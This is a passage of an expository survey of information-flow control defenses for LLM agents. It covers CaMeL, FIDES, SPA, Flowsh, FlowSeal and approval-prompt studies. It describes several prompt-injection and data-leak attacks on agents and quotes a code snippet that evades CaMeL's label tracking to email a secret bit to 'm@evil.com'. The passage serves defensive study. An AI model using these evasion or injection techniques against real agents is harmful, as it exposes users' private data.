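A label can name a group or list its members. If a budget is labeled "finance team", a new accountant may read it from the first day, but so may anyone added to the team by mistake. With a fixed list, the accountant has to wait to be added. Liu chose fixed lists, so adding a reader requires an explicit grant for a particular item. When someone leaves, the design removes them from every stored audience, starting with the next call to the model. Removal can't undo what the person has already read, and Liu did not test it.

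Sometimes the system can't identify who is present. In a small test with faulty identity data, Liu counted 13 opportunities to expose a forbidden item. A system that assumed viewers were authorized when their identity was uncertain exposed the item in 11 of them. A system that treated the audience as public exposed none, but it withheld 15 of the 43 items that the viewers were entitled to see.

### Harmless totals and revealing combinations

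The sentence "This release fixes 14 bugs" is harmless, but if the agent counted the bugs in the private repository, the number has the reader set {user, colleague}, and permitted flow keeps it out of the public release notes. Intersection cannot give a total more readers than the records behind it. Liu's first paper has the same drawback, since it withholds any summary that might draw on data meant for several audiences from everyone but the agent's owner.

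Costa and colleagues partially address this by adding a value's type to its label. They rank types by how much information each can carry, from a yes-or-no answer to a choice from a fixed list to free text. A policy could then release a small value that it would block if it were free text. A count between 0 and 1,023, for example, carries at most ten bits, far too few for a customer's name and address. But size is a poor measure of harm. The answer to "Is there an unpatched security hole?" is only one bit, yet the user would want to keep it private. And if an agent publishes the average of two people's salaries, each of them can work out the other's. A reader set can't distinguish aggregates that are safe to publish from those that aren't.

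The opposite problem is worse, because the rule allows the leak. Suppose someone at Northfield Hospital mentions in a public issue that the hospital runs version 4.1 of the software. According to a public advisory, a crafted file can take over that version. If an agent tries to help by posting a list of customers still on vulnerable versions, attackers can see which ones to target. The rule allows the post because both facts carry the label *U*, and *U* ∩ *U* = *U*.

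A better choice of reader sets would not fix this. A message passes exactly when each of its sources could have gone to the same audience alone, so labels that allow both facts separately must also allow them together. To block the list, someone would have to anticipate that particular combination and add a rule against it.

### A repository the agent has just created

Reader sets handle PixelLeak quite well, even though the agent's public repository did not exist when anyone might have written a policy. The screenshots show a private project, so they inherit that project's readers. Everyone can read the new repository, so the rule blocks the upload. The rule doesn't depend on the content, so it works on pictures as well as text.

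The strict rule may even block the call before the upload, which creates the public repository. The repository's name is public, and in the Minesweeper run the model chose it after reading the private code, so under the strict rule creating the repository is already a flow from private to public. If the agent had created the repository before opening anything private, that call would have passed and the upload would have been the first to fail.

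An agent could still create a private repository, upload the pictures and then change the setting to public. That last call contains no text from the project, so the policy engine has to treat making a repository public as releasing everything in it.

Labels taken from a repository's setting can also be wrong after a leak. If the screenshots reach the public repository by a route the policy engine doesn't cover, such as the command line, GitHub's labelled server will mark them "public" when another agent later fetches them. Permitted flow then lets that agent send a customer's billing records anywhere. The label is wrong because it reflects who can read the repository, whereas a reader set is supposed to list who is allowed to read the data.

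## Carrying labels through a language model

In an ordinary program, a policy engine can work out from the code which values depend on private data. If one line adds two private numbers and the next copies a public title, the sum is private and the title is not. A language model computes each word of its output from the whole context, so any part of the context may have affected any word, and the policy engine has no such lines of code to inspect to find out which parts did.

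The cautious rule of labeling each output with everything in the context follows from this, and Costa and colleagues add the labels of the tool descriptions. Christodorescu and colleagues see no better assumption at present and call the consequence "label explosion", in which every piece of data ends up with every label. With reader sets, the context label after step *n* is

Rₙ = Rₙ₋₁ ∩ R(*dₙ*)

where *dₙ* is whatever the agent reads at that step. The label can therefore only become stricter until the application clears the context.

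### Ten steps with one private read

Suppose the agent in the running example works through three public issues in one session. Only the user and a colleague may read the private repository.

| Step | Call | Context readers afterwards | Permitted flow |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Read issue 12, a question about installation | everyone | Passes |
| 2 | Answer issue 12 | everyone | Passes |
| 3 | Read issue 13, which asks whether the import crash is fixed | everyone | Passes |
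| 4 | `list_commits` on the private repository | {user, colleague} | Passes |
| 5 | Answer issue 13 | {user, colleague} | Blocked |
| 6 | Read issue 14, which reports a typo in the public README | {user, colleague} | Passes |
| 7 | Read the public README | {user, colleague} | Passes |
| 8 | Correct the typo | {user, colleague} | Blocked |
| 9 | Thank the person who reported it | {user, colleague} | Blocked |
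| 10 | Add a note to the private repository | {user, colleague} | Passes |

The single private read at step 4 blocks all three public writes that follow. The private history was relevant only to the answer to issue 13. The typo correction would presumably have been the same if the agent had never opened that history, but the policy engine can't establish this, because the private commits were in the model's context when it wrote the correction.

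Handling issue 13 last would have saved the other two writes. A planner can't always arrange this, because it may be unclear in advance which issue will need private data. If the private read is equally likely to occur at any of the ten steps, the read and the calls after it make up 5.5 of the ten calls on average.

An operator could also divide the work among several agents, each with its own context and label. Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026), in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, simulated such arrangements without a language model. They generated thousands of random tasks of 4 to 20 tool calls and counted how many calls introduced a sensitive label or ran under one. Agents that could pass results directly to each other spread the label least. When messages went through a central agent, that agent picked up the label too. In tasks of 20 calls,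 four of them sensitive, routing messages this way added about five percentage points to the share of affected calls.

Using more agents also helped, although the number of connections to monitor could grow with the square of the number of agents. Even the best layout left many calls with the sensitive label, because any call that needs sensitive data gets that label wherever it runs. Gregory and colleagues conclude that system design can reduce the problem but not remove it.

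### Storing results in variables

An agent can sometimes use private text without its planning model, the model that chooses the tool calls, ever receiving it. Costa and colleagues describe a planner that does this with variables. If a user asks it to send three emails to someone as a Slack message, it proceeds as follows:

1. The model calls `read_emails(number=3)`.
2. The application stores the emails under the name `#read_emails_0` and adds only that name to the context.
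3. The model calls `send_message` with `#read_emails_0` as the message.
4. The application replaces the name with the emails, and the policy engine compares their label with the recipient.

The emails keep their own label, which the policy engine checks at step 4. The context label doesn't change, so the agent can still write in public afterwards.

This works only when the model can choose its calls without knowing what the data contains. Costa and colleagues call a task data independent if one fixed sequence of calls and one final response would solve it whatever the data contained. Summarizing the emails requires something to read them, and replying only if they contain a question also requires the planner to learn whether they do.

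### The Dual LLM pattern

Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed using a second model to read untrusted text. This "quarantined" model has no tools. The "privileged" model takes instructions from the user and can call tools. An ordinary program, the controller, passes material between them.

To summarize an email, the controller fetches it and stores it as `$VAR1`. The privileged model outputs a request to summarize `$VAR1`, and the controller passes the email's text to the quarantined model. The controller stores the summary as `$VAR2` and can display it when the privileged model outputs an instruction to do so. The privileged model receives neither the email nor the summary, so instructions hidden in the email can't reach it. Willison allows one exception. The privileged model may receive the quarantined model's answer if it must come from a fixed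 set of categories, because the controller can verify that it does.

Willison designed the pattern to defend against prompt injection, but it also allows more precise labels. If the quarantined model starts each query with an empty context, its answer needs only the labels of the texts supplied for that query. The pattern itself has no labels, however, so if the privileged model instructs the controller to post the summary in `$VAR2` on a public issue, nothing checks who may read that summary.

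Its defense against injection also has a gap. Suppose a user asks the agent to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in some meeting notes. The quarantined model has to extract the address, and text planted in the notes can make it return an attacker's address instead. The agent then carries out the intended plan but sends the document to the wrong person. Willison had already called the solution "pretty bad", because it adds complexity and makes the assistant worse to use.

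*Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) treats the quarantine pattern as a special case of information-flow control. A sub-agent that has read untrusted data may still call tools, but label checks restrict which ones.

### CaMeL's fixed plan

Google DeepMind's CaMeL, published in 2025, adds the missing checks. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains how it works:

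1. The privileged model receives the user's request and writes a program in a restricted form of Python, before the agent reads any outside data.
2. An interpreter runs the program, calling tools and using a quarantined model wherever text needs reading.
3. The interpreter tags each value with its sources and permitted readers, and keeps track of which values came from which others.
4. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks the tags against that tool's policy. It can allow the call, refuse it or ask the user.

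In Bob's case, the interpreter has a record that the address came from the meeting notes. A policy can then require the user's approval unless the address is already trusted.

For the release notes, the program might be:

```
commits = list_commits(repo="private")
notes = query_quarantined_llm("Write release notes", commits)
create_or_update_file(repo="public", path="NOTES.md", content=notes)
```

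Text planted in a commit can't add a fourth line or change the repository in the third line. The variable `notes` inherits the readers {user, colleague}, so permitted flow blocks the third line. The planning model never received the commits, so a later request to correct the public README would pass. CaMeL therefore removes the accidental blocks from the ten-step session, but the release notes remain blocked because they come from the private history.

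A plan written in advance also makes the agent less flexible. The privileged model has to foresee every branch, so it can't read an issue, notice that it depends on another and decide to open that one too. Somebody must write and maintain the policies, and Willison, who has worked in application security for two decades, is nervous about any design that requires ordinary users to do this.

### FIDES, step by step

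FIDES, the planner that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, keeps the usual loop, in which the model chooses each call after the previous result. It hides a result only when showing it would make the context label stricter:

- If ℓ(result) ⊑ ℓ(context), the application adds the result to the context.
- Otherwise, it stores the result in a variable and adds only the variable's name.

The application applies this rule to each field separately, so the model might receive an email's date but not its body.

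The planner has two tools for finding out what a variable contains. It can use `query_llm` to ask an isolated model a question, and can require the answer to be in a particular format, such as yes or no. The application stores the answer in a new variable, which carries the labels of everything used to produce it. The planner can also use `inspect` to bring a variable's contents into its context, but it then takes on the stricter label. Because labels include a value's type, a policy can treat a yes-or-no answer more leniently than free text.

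In Costa and colleagues' example, a user asks the agent to read three emails, check whether any requests a meeting, and create a calendar event if so. The table traces the integrity label through these steps.

| Step | Call | What enters the planner's context | Context label afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `read_emails(number=3)` | the name `#read_emails_0` | trusted |
| 2 | `query_llm`: is there a meeting request? (yes or no) | the name `#query_llm_0` | trusted |
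| 3 | `inspect(#query_llm_0)` | `true` | untrusted, but only a yes-or-no value |
| 4 | `query_llm`: extract the event details | the name `#query_llm_1` | unchanged |
| 5 | `set_event(#query_llm_1)` | confirmation, if the policy allows the call | |

At step 5, the decision to create an event depends on untrusted text, so a strict policy would block it. Costa and colleagues suggest a looser policy that allows a single yes-or-no answer to influence the decision, since one bit is unlikely to carry an injected instruction. Whoever wrote the email could still add a false meeting to the calendar, but could not use the email to make the planner forward the mailbox.

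The isolated model reads all three emails together, so the event details can have the same problem as the replies from Alex's inbox. Permitted flow may block an invitation even to the person who proposed the meeting, unless the planner queries each email separately.

### The 2025 results on AgentDojo

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES in 2025 on AgentDojo's 97 ordinary tasks, using OpenAI's GPT-4o and o1. The basic agent in the table puts every result straight into its context. The figures show the percentage of tasks each agent completed when there was no attack, averaged over five runs.

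| Model and agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o, basic, no policy checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| GPT-4o, basic, with checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| GPT-4o, FIDES, with checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |
| o1, basic, no policy checks | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 |
| o1, basic, with checks | 48.0 | 75.0 | 37.5 | 17.1 |
| o1, FIDES, with checks | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 |

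An accumulating label can greatly reduce the number of tasks an agent completes. In the Slack column, the checks lowered the basic agent's completion rate with GPT-4o from 93% to 20%, and FIDES recovered a little over a third of the loss. On average across the four settings, FIDES completed about 8 percentage points more tasks than the basic agent under the same checks with GPT-4o, and 16 more with o1.

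In the attack tests with GPT-4o, 152 planted instructions succeeded against the basic agent without checks, and 21 succeeded against FIDES without checks. With checks, none succeeded against either agent, after the researchers excluded cases that AgentDojo misjudged. So the checks provided the security, and hiding results mainly let the agent complete more tasks.

The zero may not hold in a real deployment, because the researchers labeled as untrusted every field that AgentDojo's attacks use. A real deployment would have to label fields without knowing where the attacks will be. The tests also hid data only on the basis of integrity. The policies enforced confidentiality, but the researchers did not test how well FIDES works when it hides private data. Developers have since released much stronger models, which may handle variables better but still can't complete tasks that the policy forbids,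 such as the many banking tasks in which the agent has to follow instructions in a file.

*Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL eliminated nearly all of AgentDojo's attacks with comparable task performance. Later tests found a larger loss in task performance. *SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a competing defense, tested an adapted version of CaMeL's released code. None of 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks, while SecureClaw completed 59. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports that turning on CaMeL's policy checks halved its utility on the banking tasks. The results may differ partly because of whether the policy checks were on, and partly because *SecureClaw* adapted the code.

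### What an agent reveals by choosing

Costa and colleagues prove that their label tracking can enforce a property called explicit secrecy. Let *d*₁ and *d*₂ be two states of the world that look the same to an outsider and differ only in private data. Let *g*₁ be the sequence of tool calls the agent makes when it starts from *d*₁, and *g*₂ the sequence it makes from *d*₂. With ≈ for "looks the same to an outsider", the two standards are:

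Explicit secrecy: *g*₁(*d*₁) ≈ *g*₁(*d*₂)

Noninterference: *g*₁(*d*₁) ≈ *g*₂(*d*₂)

Explicit secrecy requires the visible result to stay the same when the same calls are replayed on different private data. It rules out copying private text into a public comment, because the comment would change with the text. Noninterference also covers the different calls the agent might have made if the private data had been different, so the agent's choice of calls must not reveal anything about that data either.

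Suppose a public web page contains two standard replies, "We are still working on this" and "This will be fixed in the next release". The agent stores them in variables labeled public and untrusted. It then checks a private fact, whether the fix is finished, and posts the second reply. The posted text was already public, so the message passes a confidentiality check. Replaying the call with the private fact reversed would post the same sentence, so explicit secrecy holds. But the agent would have chosen the other reply if the fact were reversed, so a stranger who knows how the agent works learns the fact from the post.

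Costa and colleagues considered noninterference too restrictive for their planner because it would essentially forbid any call with publicly visible effects after any call that may read private data, the rule that blocked the typo correction. Their guarantee depends on correct labels and on checking every call, and it doesn't cover timing or the length of network messages. It also doesn't ensure that the text is accurate, since an injected instruction can still corrupt a summary without changing who receives it.

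CaMeL does track some choices. If a program sends an email only when a bank balance is above a threshold, the interpreter treats the email as dependent on the balance and blocks it. Garby and colleagues found a way around this, using a trick known since the 1970s:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
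```

When the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and private, and the program skips the line that would set `rich` to false. CaMeL raises a variable's label only on the branch that runs. `rich` therefore keeps its public label, even though its value now depends on the balance, and the program sends the email. When the balance is low, the program sends nothing.

An attacker would normally have trouble getting CaMeL's planning model to write this program, because the model doesn't read untrusted data. Still, the example shows that CaMeL's tracking does not guarantee noninterference. Garby and colleagues describe another leak, in the code that reruns a program after a failure. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, and repeated attempts can reveal the whole secret one bit at a time. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) had already listed side channels as a gap and a machine-checked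 proof of noninterference as future work.

Garby and colleagues provide such a proof for every program in a small programming language they designed, including agents that write and run code. In their version of noninterference, secrets can't affect the probabilities of public results, except by affecting whether the program finishes. The language avoids some label accumulation by letting a program ask a question in a temporary copy of the conversation and then return to the original. An agent written in the language resisted the attack in all but two of 1,296 attacked runs on AgentDojo's banking tasks, and completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did with its policy checks turned off.

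### Labels that outlast the session

Many agents keep notes between requests, and these notes can carry private or untrusted text into a context that looks clean. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) gives the example of an agent that saves an invoice containing an attacker's account number. The next day, the user asks it to "pay the invoice we discussed yesterday."

In their system, also called SPA, the planning model writes one complete plan for each request, using only six kinds of step. A checker follows the labels through the whole plan before any tool runs. Each step inside a condition inherits that condition's label, and the checker examines both branches. SPA would therefore reject a plan that chose between two public replies based on a private fact. If the checker rejects a plan, the request fails, and the planning model gets no feedback it could use to try again.

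SPA stores each result with its label. For a later request, the planner receives a description of the stored result, such as its format and what it represents, but not the value. SPA supplies the value, with its original label, only while the plan is running. On Tuesday the agent can find the invoice, but the account number is still untrusted, so a payment policy can block it.

SPA reduced the attack success rate to zero on AgentDojo. The rate was 0.2% on a version that Girrens and Wang extended to several connected requests. Turning on the label checks reduced task completion from 53.0% to 29.0% on the original benchmark and from 62.5% to 35.3% on the extended one. Most of the loss came from integrity checks on tasks that legitimately depend on outside data. When a later request needed a stored result that was available, the agent retrieved it 95.4% of the time without the checks and 89.9%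 with them.

### Shell commands

Coding agents do much of their work through a command shell, where a single script can read a private file and upload it without the text entering the model's context. The context label then doesn't reflect this transfer. *Flowsh* therefore gives each command its own label, which starts as the agent's context label and becomes stricter as the command reads files or receives data from the network.

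Flowsh runs the command in a sandbox and monitors what the command opens. It keeps changes to files in a separate layer until the command finishes, then applies them if the policy or the user allows them. It can't undo a network request, so a proxy checks each one before sending it. Flowsh also saves labels with the files, and a command run in a later session inherits them.

Flowsh labels individual commands instead of a whole conversation, but its rule is just as cautious. It doesn't analyze what a program does with its inputs, so a command that searches a private folder and a public one gets the label of both.

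The researchers compared Flowsh with a loosely configured sandbox that asked for approval whenever it couldn't guarantee safety. On 17 office tasks, Flowsh needed 5.8 times fewer approvals per completed task, but its completion rate was 7.9 percentage points lower. On Terminal-Bench, a set of command-line tasks, it needed 22.5 times fewer approvals, and its completion rate was 9.7 points lower. In a setting without approvals, no attack succeeded in the 19 cases tested, even when the attacker fully controlled the model's output after the injection.

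Flowsh could cover the command-line route that many of the earlier controls leave open in PixelLeak. Its policy would still need to distinguish public repositories from private ones, because the agent reaches both through GitHub.

### A model that judges where text came from

*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) shows that an agent's choices can leak private data in practice. In one attack, an outsider gives the agent a shared page that mixes real private records with invented ones and asks it to clean up the page. The agent refuses to delete some entries, and its refusals reveal which records are real, even though it writes no private text.

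FlowSeal, a defense published in September 2026, labels private records by owner and origin. A program outside the agent's context intercepts every tool call that writes or shares something. When necessary, it uses an isolated model to check whether the proposed output discloses any protected records. This model doesn't receive the agent's conversation, so an outsider can't influence it by presenting the request as ordinary teamwork.

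FlowSeal reduced the leak rate from 52.2% to 0.5% in an attack that asked the agent to fill in its part of a shared document. Across all the tests with FlowSeal, between 0 and 3.3% of private items leaked, and the agent completed 72.4% of ordinary tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best alternative. With live Gmail and Notion accounts, the clean-up attack leaked 34.7% of items under a prompt-based defense and none under FlowSeal.

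Shim and colleagues prove that private data can't reach a less protected place without passing the release check, but they don't prove that the isolated model's judgment is right. They also exclude prompt injection from the attacks they consider, so their results don't show how FlowSeal would handle the planted issue in Invariant's demonstration. An injected instruction could conceivably reach the isolated model as part of the proposed output.

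In the ten-step session, this kind of judge could allow the typo correction even with the private commits in the context, as well as release notes that read only "Bug fixes". The good note about the import crash is a harder case because it paraphrases a private record, and a judge that checks only whether the note came from that record should find that it did.

### Estimates in place of labels

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* proposes replacing all-or-nothing labels with estimates of how much each input influenced an output. One method is to remove an input and measure the change in what the model does. A simple version of the measure is

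influence of *d* = distance between P(action | context) and P(action | context without *d*)

If the typo correction is equally likely with and without the private commits, the commits have almost no influence on it, and it could keep a public label. Researchers might also estimate influence from the model's internals.

On an agent using the Qwen3-8B model, *Sightline* (2026) used such estimates to remove 50.0% of the labels that the cautious rule attaches from inputs that did not affect a call. Its method missed a real flow in 3.9% of episodes. It kept the labels in almost all the attack cases, and no attack got past an integrity policy that used them.

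The objection is that an estimate can't support the same guarantee. Christodorescu and colleagues argue that patient attackers will find the failures in probabilistic monitors, as Willison argued about attack detectors. Errors accumulate even without an attacker. If misses were independent, an agent with a 3.9% miss rate would have about a 98% chance of at least one miss in 100 episodes. Many misses would be harmless, since a wrong label causes a leak only if the agent then sends the data to someone who shouldn't have it.

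How much this matters depends on the threat. In PixelLeak, nobody was searching for a weakness, and an estimate that caught most of the uploads would have been much better than no label. For an agent that reads issues from strangers, a rare failure that an attacker can repeat is much more serious.

Costa and colleagues describe a method that keeps more of the guarantee. It estimates which messages matter, then has the model write the response again with only those messages in its context. If those messages don't include the private commits, the new response can't copy from the commits, even if the estimate was poor. The choice of messages may still reveal a little about the private data.

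None of these methods would allow the notes about the import crash to be released. The model needs the private history to write them, so even a perfect measure of influence would show that the notes depend on it.

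## Deciding when private data may be released

Under the permitted flow rule, data may be released only if everyone in the audience is already entitled to read it. This blocks release notes drawn from private records and many replies to customers. The problem is much older than agents. Sabelfeld and Sands point out in *Declassification* that even a failed login reveals that the password isn't the one just tried. A useful system therefore needs exceptions, and somebody has to decide when they apply.

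### Declassification and endorsement

Declassification is a deliberate decision to let data reach readers whom its label excludes. Myers, Sabelfeld and Zdancewic, in *Enforcing Robust Declassification and Qualified Robustness*, write it as an operation, `declassify(e, ℓ)`, which returns the value of *e* unchanged but gives it the new label ℓ. If the draft release notes name Northfield Hospital, they still name it after declassification, and now everyone may read them.

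Endorsement, the counterpart for trust, relabels untrusted data as trusted, again without changing it. A maintainer endorses a stranger's issue by reading it and marking it `approved` for GitHub's integrity filter.

Sabelfeld and Sands sort release policies by what they let out, who can cause the release, where in the system it happens and when. A policy that restricts only one of these can fail on another. Suppose a shop may log at most four digits of a credit card number per purchase. An attacker who can choose which four can collect the whole number over a few purchases.

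### Keeping attackers out of the decision

Robust declassification, an idea that Myers and colleagues credit to Zdancewic and Myers, concerns who can cause a release. An attacker must be able to affect neither what the system releases nor whether it releases anything. Their example is one line long:

```
if x then y := declassify(z)
```

Here `z` is secret and `y` is public. An attacker who can change `x` controls whether the secret is released, and one who can copy a different secret into `z` controls which secret is released. The release is robust only if the attacker can do neither.

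An attacker who interferes should learn no more than one who only watches. *Demystifying Information Flow Downgrading using the Real-Ideal Paradigm* (Kanniwadi and Myers, 2026) gives the example *p* := *u* × *s*, where *p* is public, *s* is secret and an attacker controls *u*. Someone watching *p* learns nothing about *s* while *u* is 0, but an attacker who sets *u* to 1 can read *s* directly. The planted issue in Invariant's demonstration worked like *u*, since it was input the attacker controlled and used to get private data released.

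Some harmless systems fail this test. Myers and colleagues describe a seller of information whose customers choose which of two secret items to buy. An untrusted buyer's choice determines what the system releases, but the seller doesn't mind as long as the buyer pays. They solve this by endorsing the choice. A support agent that answers strangers from private documentation is similar, since each question affects which passage the agent uses.

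Attackers can exploit endorsement too. In a sealed-bid auction described by Kanniwadi and Myers, Bob can't read Alice's bid, but a badly labeled program lets him set his own bid to hers plus one. The auctioneer then endorses Bob's bid, and Bob wins by the smallest possible margin. Transparent endorsement prevents this by requiring that whoever supplies a value could already read what went into it. *Nonmalleable Information Flow* (2017) treats the two conditions as symmetric: untrusted data must not influence what a system declassifies, and secrets must not influence what it endorses.

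### Microsoft's rule for a Teams channel

Microsoft has published a sample rule that applies robust declassification to agents posting in Teams, its workplace chat service. Before each post, a policy engine takes the context label and the message's reader set R, and looks up the channel's current members M. It then works out who would be reading something new to them:

missing = M ∖ R

The engine goes through these conditions in order and stops at the first that holds:

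| Condition | Decision |
|---|---|
| The context is trusted | Allow |
| *missing* is empty, so every member may already read the content | Allow |
| *missing* has someone in it | Ask the user, listing the new readers |
| None of these holds | Deny |

The denial presumably applies only when the engine can't work out *missing*, for instance because the member lookup failed.

Suppose Alex's agent has read Priya's email about the quarterly sales and wants to post a summary in a channel that includes Marco. If the engine treats email as untrusted, the trusted-context condition fails, and because Marco is in *missing*, the engine asks Alex. If the figures came instead from a trusted file that Marco isn't allowed to open, and the agent had read nothing untrusted, the engine would let the message go out without asking Alex. The reasoning is that without untrusted content, no prompt injection can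 have caused the release.

As written, the trusted-context condition seems to cover only half of the definition. It checks whether the agent decided to post in a trusted context, but not where the message text came from. In a design like FIDES, which keeps untrusted text in variables, the planner's context can be trusted even though an isolated model wrote the message after reading a stranger's email. If that model had also read a private file, the stranger could influence what the message reveals. In the version Kolluri and colleagues describe, a designer can also require particular arguments to be trusted, which would close this gap.

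### The rule applied to PixelLeak

In the PixelLeak laboratory run, the only instructions Glow describes came from the developer. The agent worked on a private repository, and Microsoft's labels for GitHub classify private repositories as trusted. The context would therefore have been trusted, and the rule would have allowed the upload without comparing the readers.

This is an inference from the published rule. The sample covers Teams messages, and a rule for GitHub uploads might differ. But the result follows from the definition of robustness, which compares an active attacker with a passive one. Sabelfeld and Sands note that without active attackers, declassification is "vacuously robust". The Minesweeper agent would have been safer if it had read a stranger's web page about image hosting, because its context would then have been untrusted and the engine would have asked the developer.

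A trusted context shows that no outsider asked for the release, but not that the user wanted it. Microsoft's rule of thumb is that anything an agent can do for a user can also happen through a model's mistake or a prompt injection. Requiring a trusted context guards against prompt injection but not against the model's mistakes. Kolluri and colleagues acknowledge that information-flow control can replace human approval for security purposes but not in general.

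An operator worried about mistakes could delete the trusted-context condition. The engine would then have asked the Minesweeper developer whether everyone on the internet should be able to see the pictures, but it would also ask about every set of release notes and many messages that users had explicitly requested. A compromise would be to skip the question only when the user's request names the audience. The request for release notes names the public repository, while the Minesweeper request, as Glow describes it, mentioned no public place. This rule would still let the agent publish the bad release note along with the good one.

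### What people do when asked

Asking the user for permission helps only if the user considers the answer. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of trouble with agents and files, and found that problems with user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 cases the user had let the agent act without prompts, sometimes through a "YOLO mode" that spares users hundreds of prompts per session. In 31 cases, some of them among the 80, the prompt didn't show what the action would do. A request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it runs whatever the script contains.

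According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), "always allow" settings reduce fatigue but "silently widen the trusted surface", and most approval prompts in existing products show a raw command on a single line. Some tools, such as GitHub's Copilot CLI and OpenAI's Codex, distinguish a single approval from one that lasts for a session or longer. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, warns against treating repeated approvals as a sign of growing trust, since they may reflect tiredness or pressure to deliver. It also notes that agents look for another route after a refusal. A refusal should therefore cover the outcome, such as making private pictures public, and not only the rejected command.

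The prompt in Microsoft's sample rule shows who would gain access, but only as a list of ID numbers, and it doesn't show where the content came from. Microsoft suggests that better dialogs could show which data the agent is sharing more widely and with whom.

Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, tested how much such information helps. In their leading example, a user wants an agent to send an auditor only summary totals. Instructions hidden in a vendor's note lead the agent to copy the raw invoice rows into `report.csv`, and the agent then asks to send that file to the auditor. The tool, the recipient and the file name all look fine. Their prompt quotes the user's original restriction, shows the exact file and recipient, and states that the attachment was built from raw invoice rows, with a link to the recorded events that support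 this statement. A monitor outside the agent records these events, so the record doesn't depend on the agent's account of what it did.

Eighty volunteers made 12 decisions each, half of them on unsafe requests. Each volunteer used one of four prompts:

| The prompt shows | Unsafe requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
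| The exact arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Also the user's instruction and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, arranged around the consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

Most of the improvement came from giving people more information. Arranging it better may have also helped, but the adjusted difference of 7.9 percentage points has a 95% interval that includes zero. When a violation depended on a chain of several steps, both of the fuller prompts led to 7 unsafe approvals out of 30. The volunteers also knew their task was to judge requests, and half of the requests were unsafe, so someone at work who sees one bad request in a thousand would probably do worse.

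### PRUDENTIA: asking less often

One response to fatigue is to have the agent plan its work so that fewer actions need approval. Kolluri and colleagues built such an agent, PRUDENTIA, on top of FIDES. The model receives the labels and policies, and must first justify opening any variable of untrusted text. It can also ask the user to endorse the text. If a harmless email contains a ten-item to-do list, the user can endorse the email once instead of approving ten separate actions.

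They propose two measures of how much an agent relies on its user. Let τᵢ be the sequence of tool calls the agent makes on task *i*, and *v*(τᵢ) the number of those calls that fail the policy and so need approval. For *n* tasks:

HITL load = Σ *v*(τᵢ), summed over the tasks the agent completes

TCR@*k* = (number of tasks completed with *v*(τᵢ) ≤ *k*) / *n*

HITL stands for "human in the loop" and TCR for "task completion rate". If an agent completes three of four tasks, needing 0, 1 and 4 approvals, its HITL load is 5. Its TCR@0 is 25%, TCR@1 is 50% and TCR@4 is 75%. Kolluri and colleagues measure both without attacks and assume that the user approves every request.

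With GPT-5 on AgentDojo, the averages over five runs were:

| Agent | Completed with unlimited approvals | HITL load | TCR@0 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Basic, asks before every consequential call | 72.3% | 52.0 | 35.1% |
| Basic, asks only when a label check fails | 72.3% | 40.4 | 43.4% |
| FIDES | 78.9% | 41.3 | 57.1% |
| PRUDENTIA | 80.0% | 7.3 | 72.7% |

The benefit depends on the model. With the older GPT-4o, PRUDENTIA had a higher load than FIDES (23.8 against 7.8) and a lower TCR@0 (42.5% against 50.3%).

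WASP, a benchmark for agents that use a web browser, plants instructions on simulated GitLab and Reddit pages. These instructions diverted the basic agent in 14.6% to 61.1% of cases, depending on the model and the site. None diverted PRUDENTIA, which had a human-in-the-loop (HITL) load of zero. The tasks suited PRUDENTIA well, though, because the agent only had to post a comment or upvote a post, so it never needed to read the untrusted text.

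An agent can have a low HITL load and still release data it shouldn't. The policy behind these figures makes the same exception for trusted contexts as the Teams rule, so private data sent from a trusted context doesn't add to the load. Under this policy, the PixelLeak upload would count as a task completed without help.

PRUDENTIA can ask the user to endorse data but not to declassify it. Kolluri and colleagues left this out because whether a release is appropriate depends heavily on the situation, and approving individual calls accounts for that better than blanket declassification does. The release notes example supports that choice. If the user declassified the whole commit history so that the agent could write the notes, the agent could also publish the customer's name or mention the unpatched security hole in a reply to a stranger.

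### GAAP: remembering the answers

Stanley, Verma and colleagues (2026), in *An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data*, describe GAAP, which requires the user's permission for each combination of a private item and an outside party. It works as follows:

1. As in CaMeL, the model writes a program for the task. The program refers to private items by name, such as "date of birth", and the model doesn't receive their values unless the user permits it.
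2. GAAP runs the program and tracks which values come from which private items. Files and other tool results count as private by default.
3. Before a call sends data out, GAAP looks up each pair of item and recipient in a permission database.
4. If the database has an answer, GAAP allows or refuses the call. If not, it asks the user and stores the answer, unless the user chooses "just once".
5. GAAP logs the disclosure. If an airline later returns a passport number that the user gave it, the log lets GAAP recognize that the airline's reply may contain the passport number.

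The database starts empty. The quality of GAAP's questions depends on annotations, which describe each tool and identify the recipient and the data the tool may return. Annotations let GAAP ask whether to share `feedback.txt` with one address, when it might otherwise ask whether to share everything in the file system with everyone the email server can reach.

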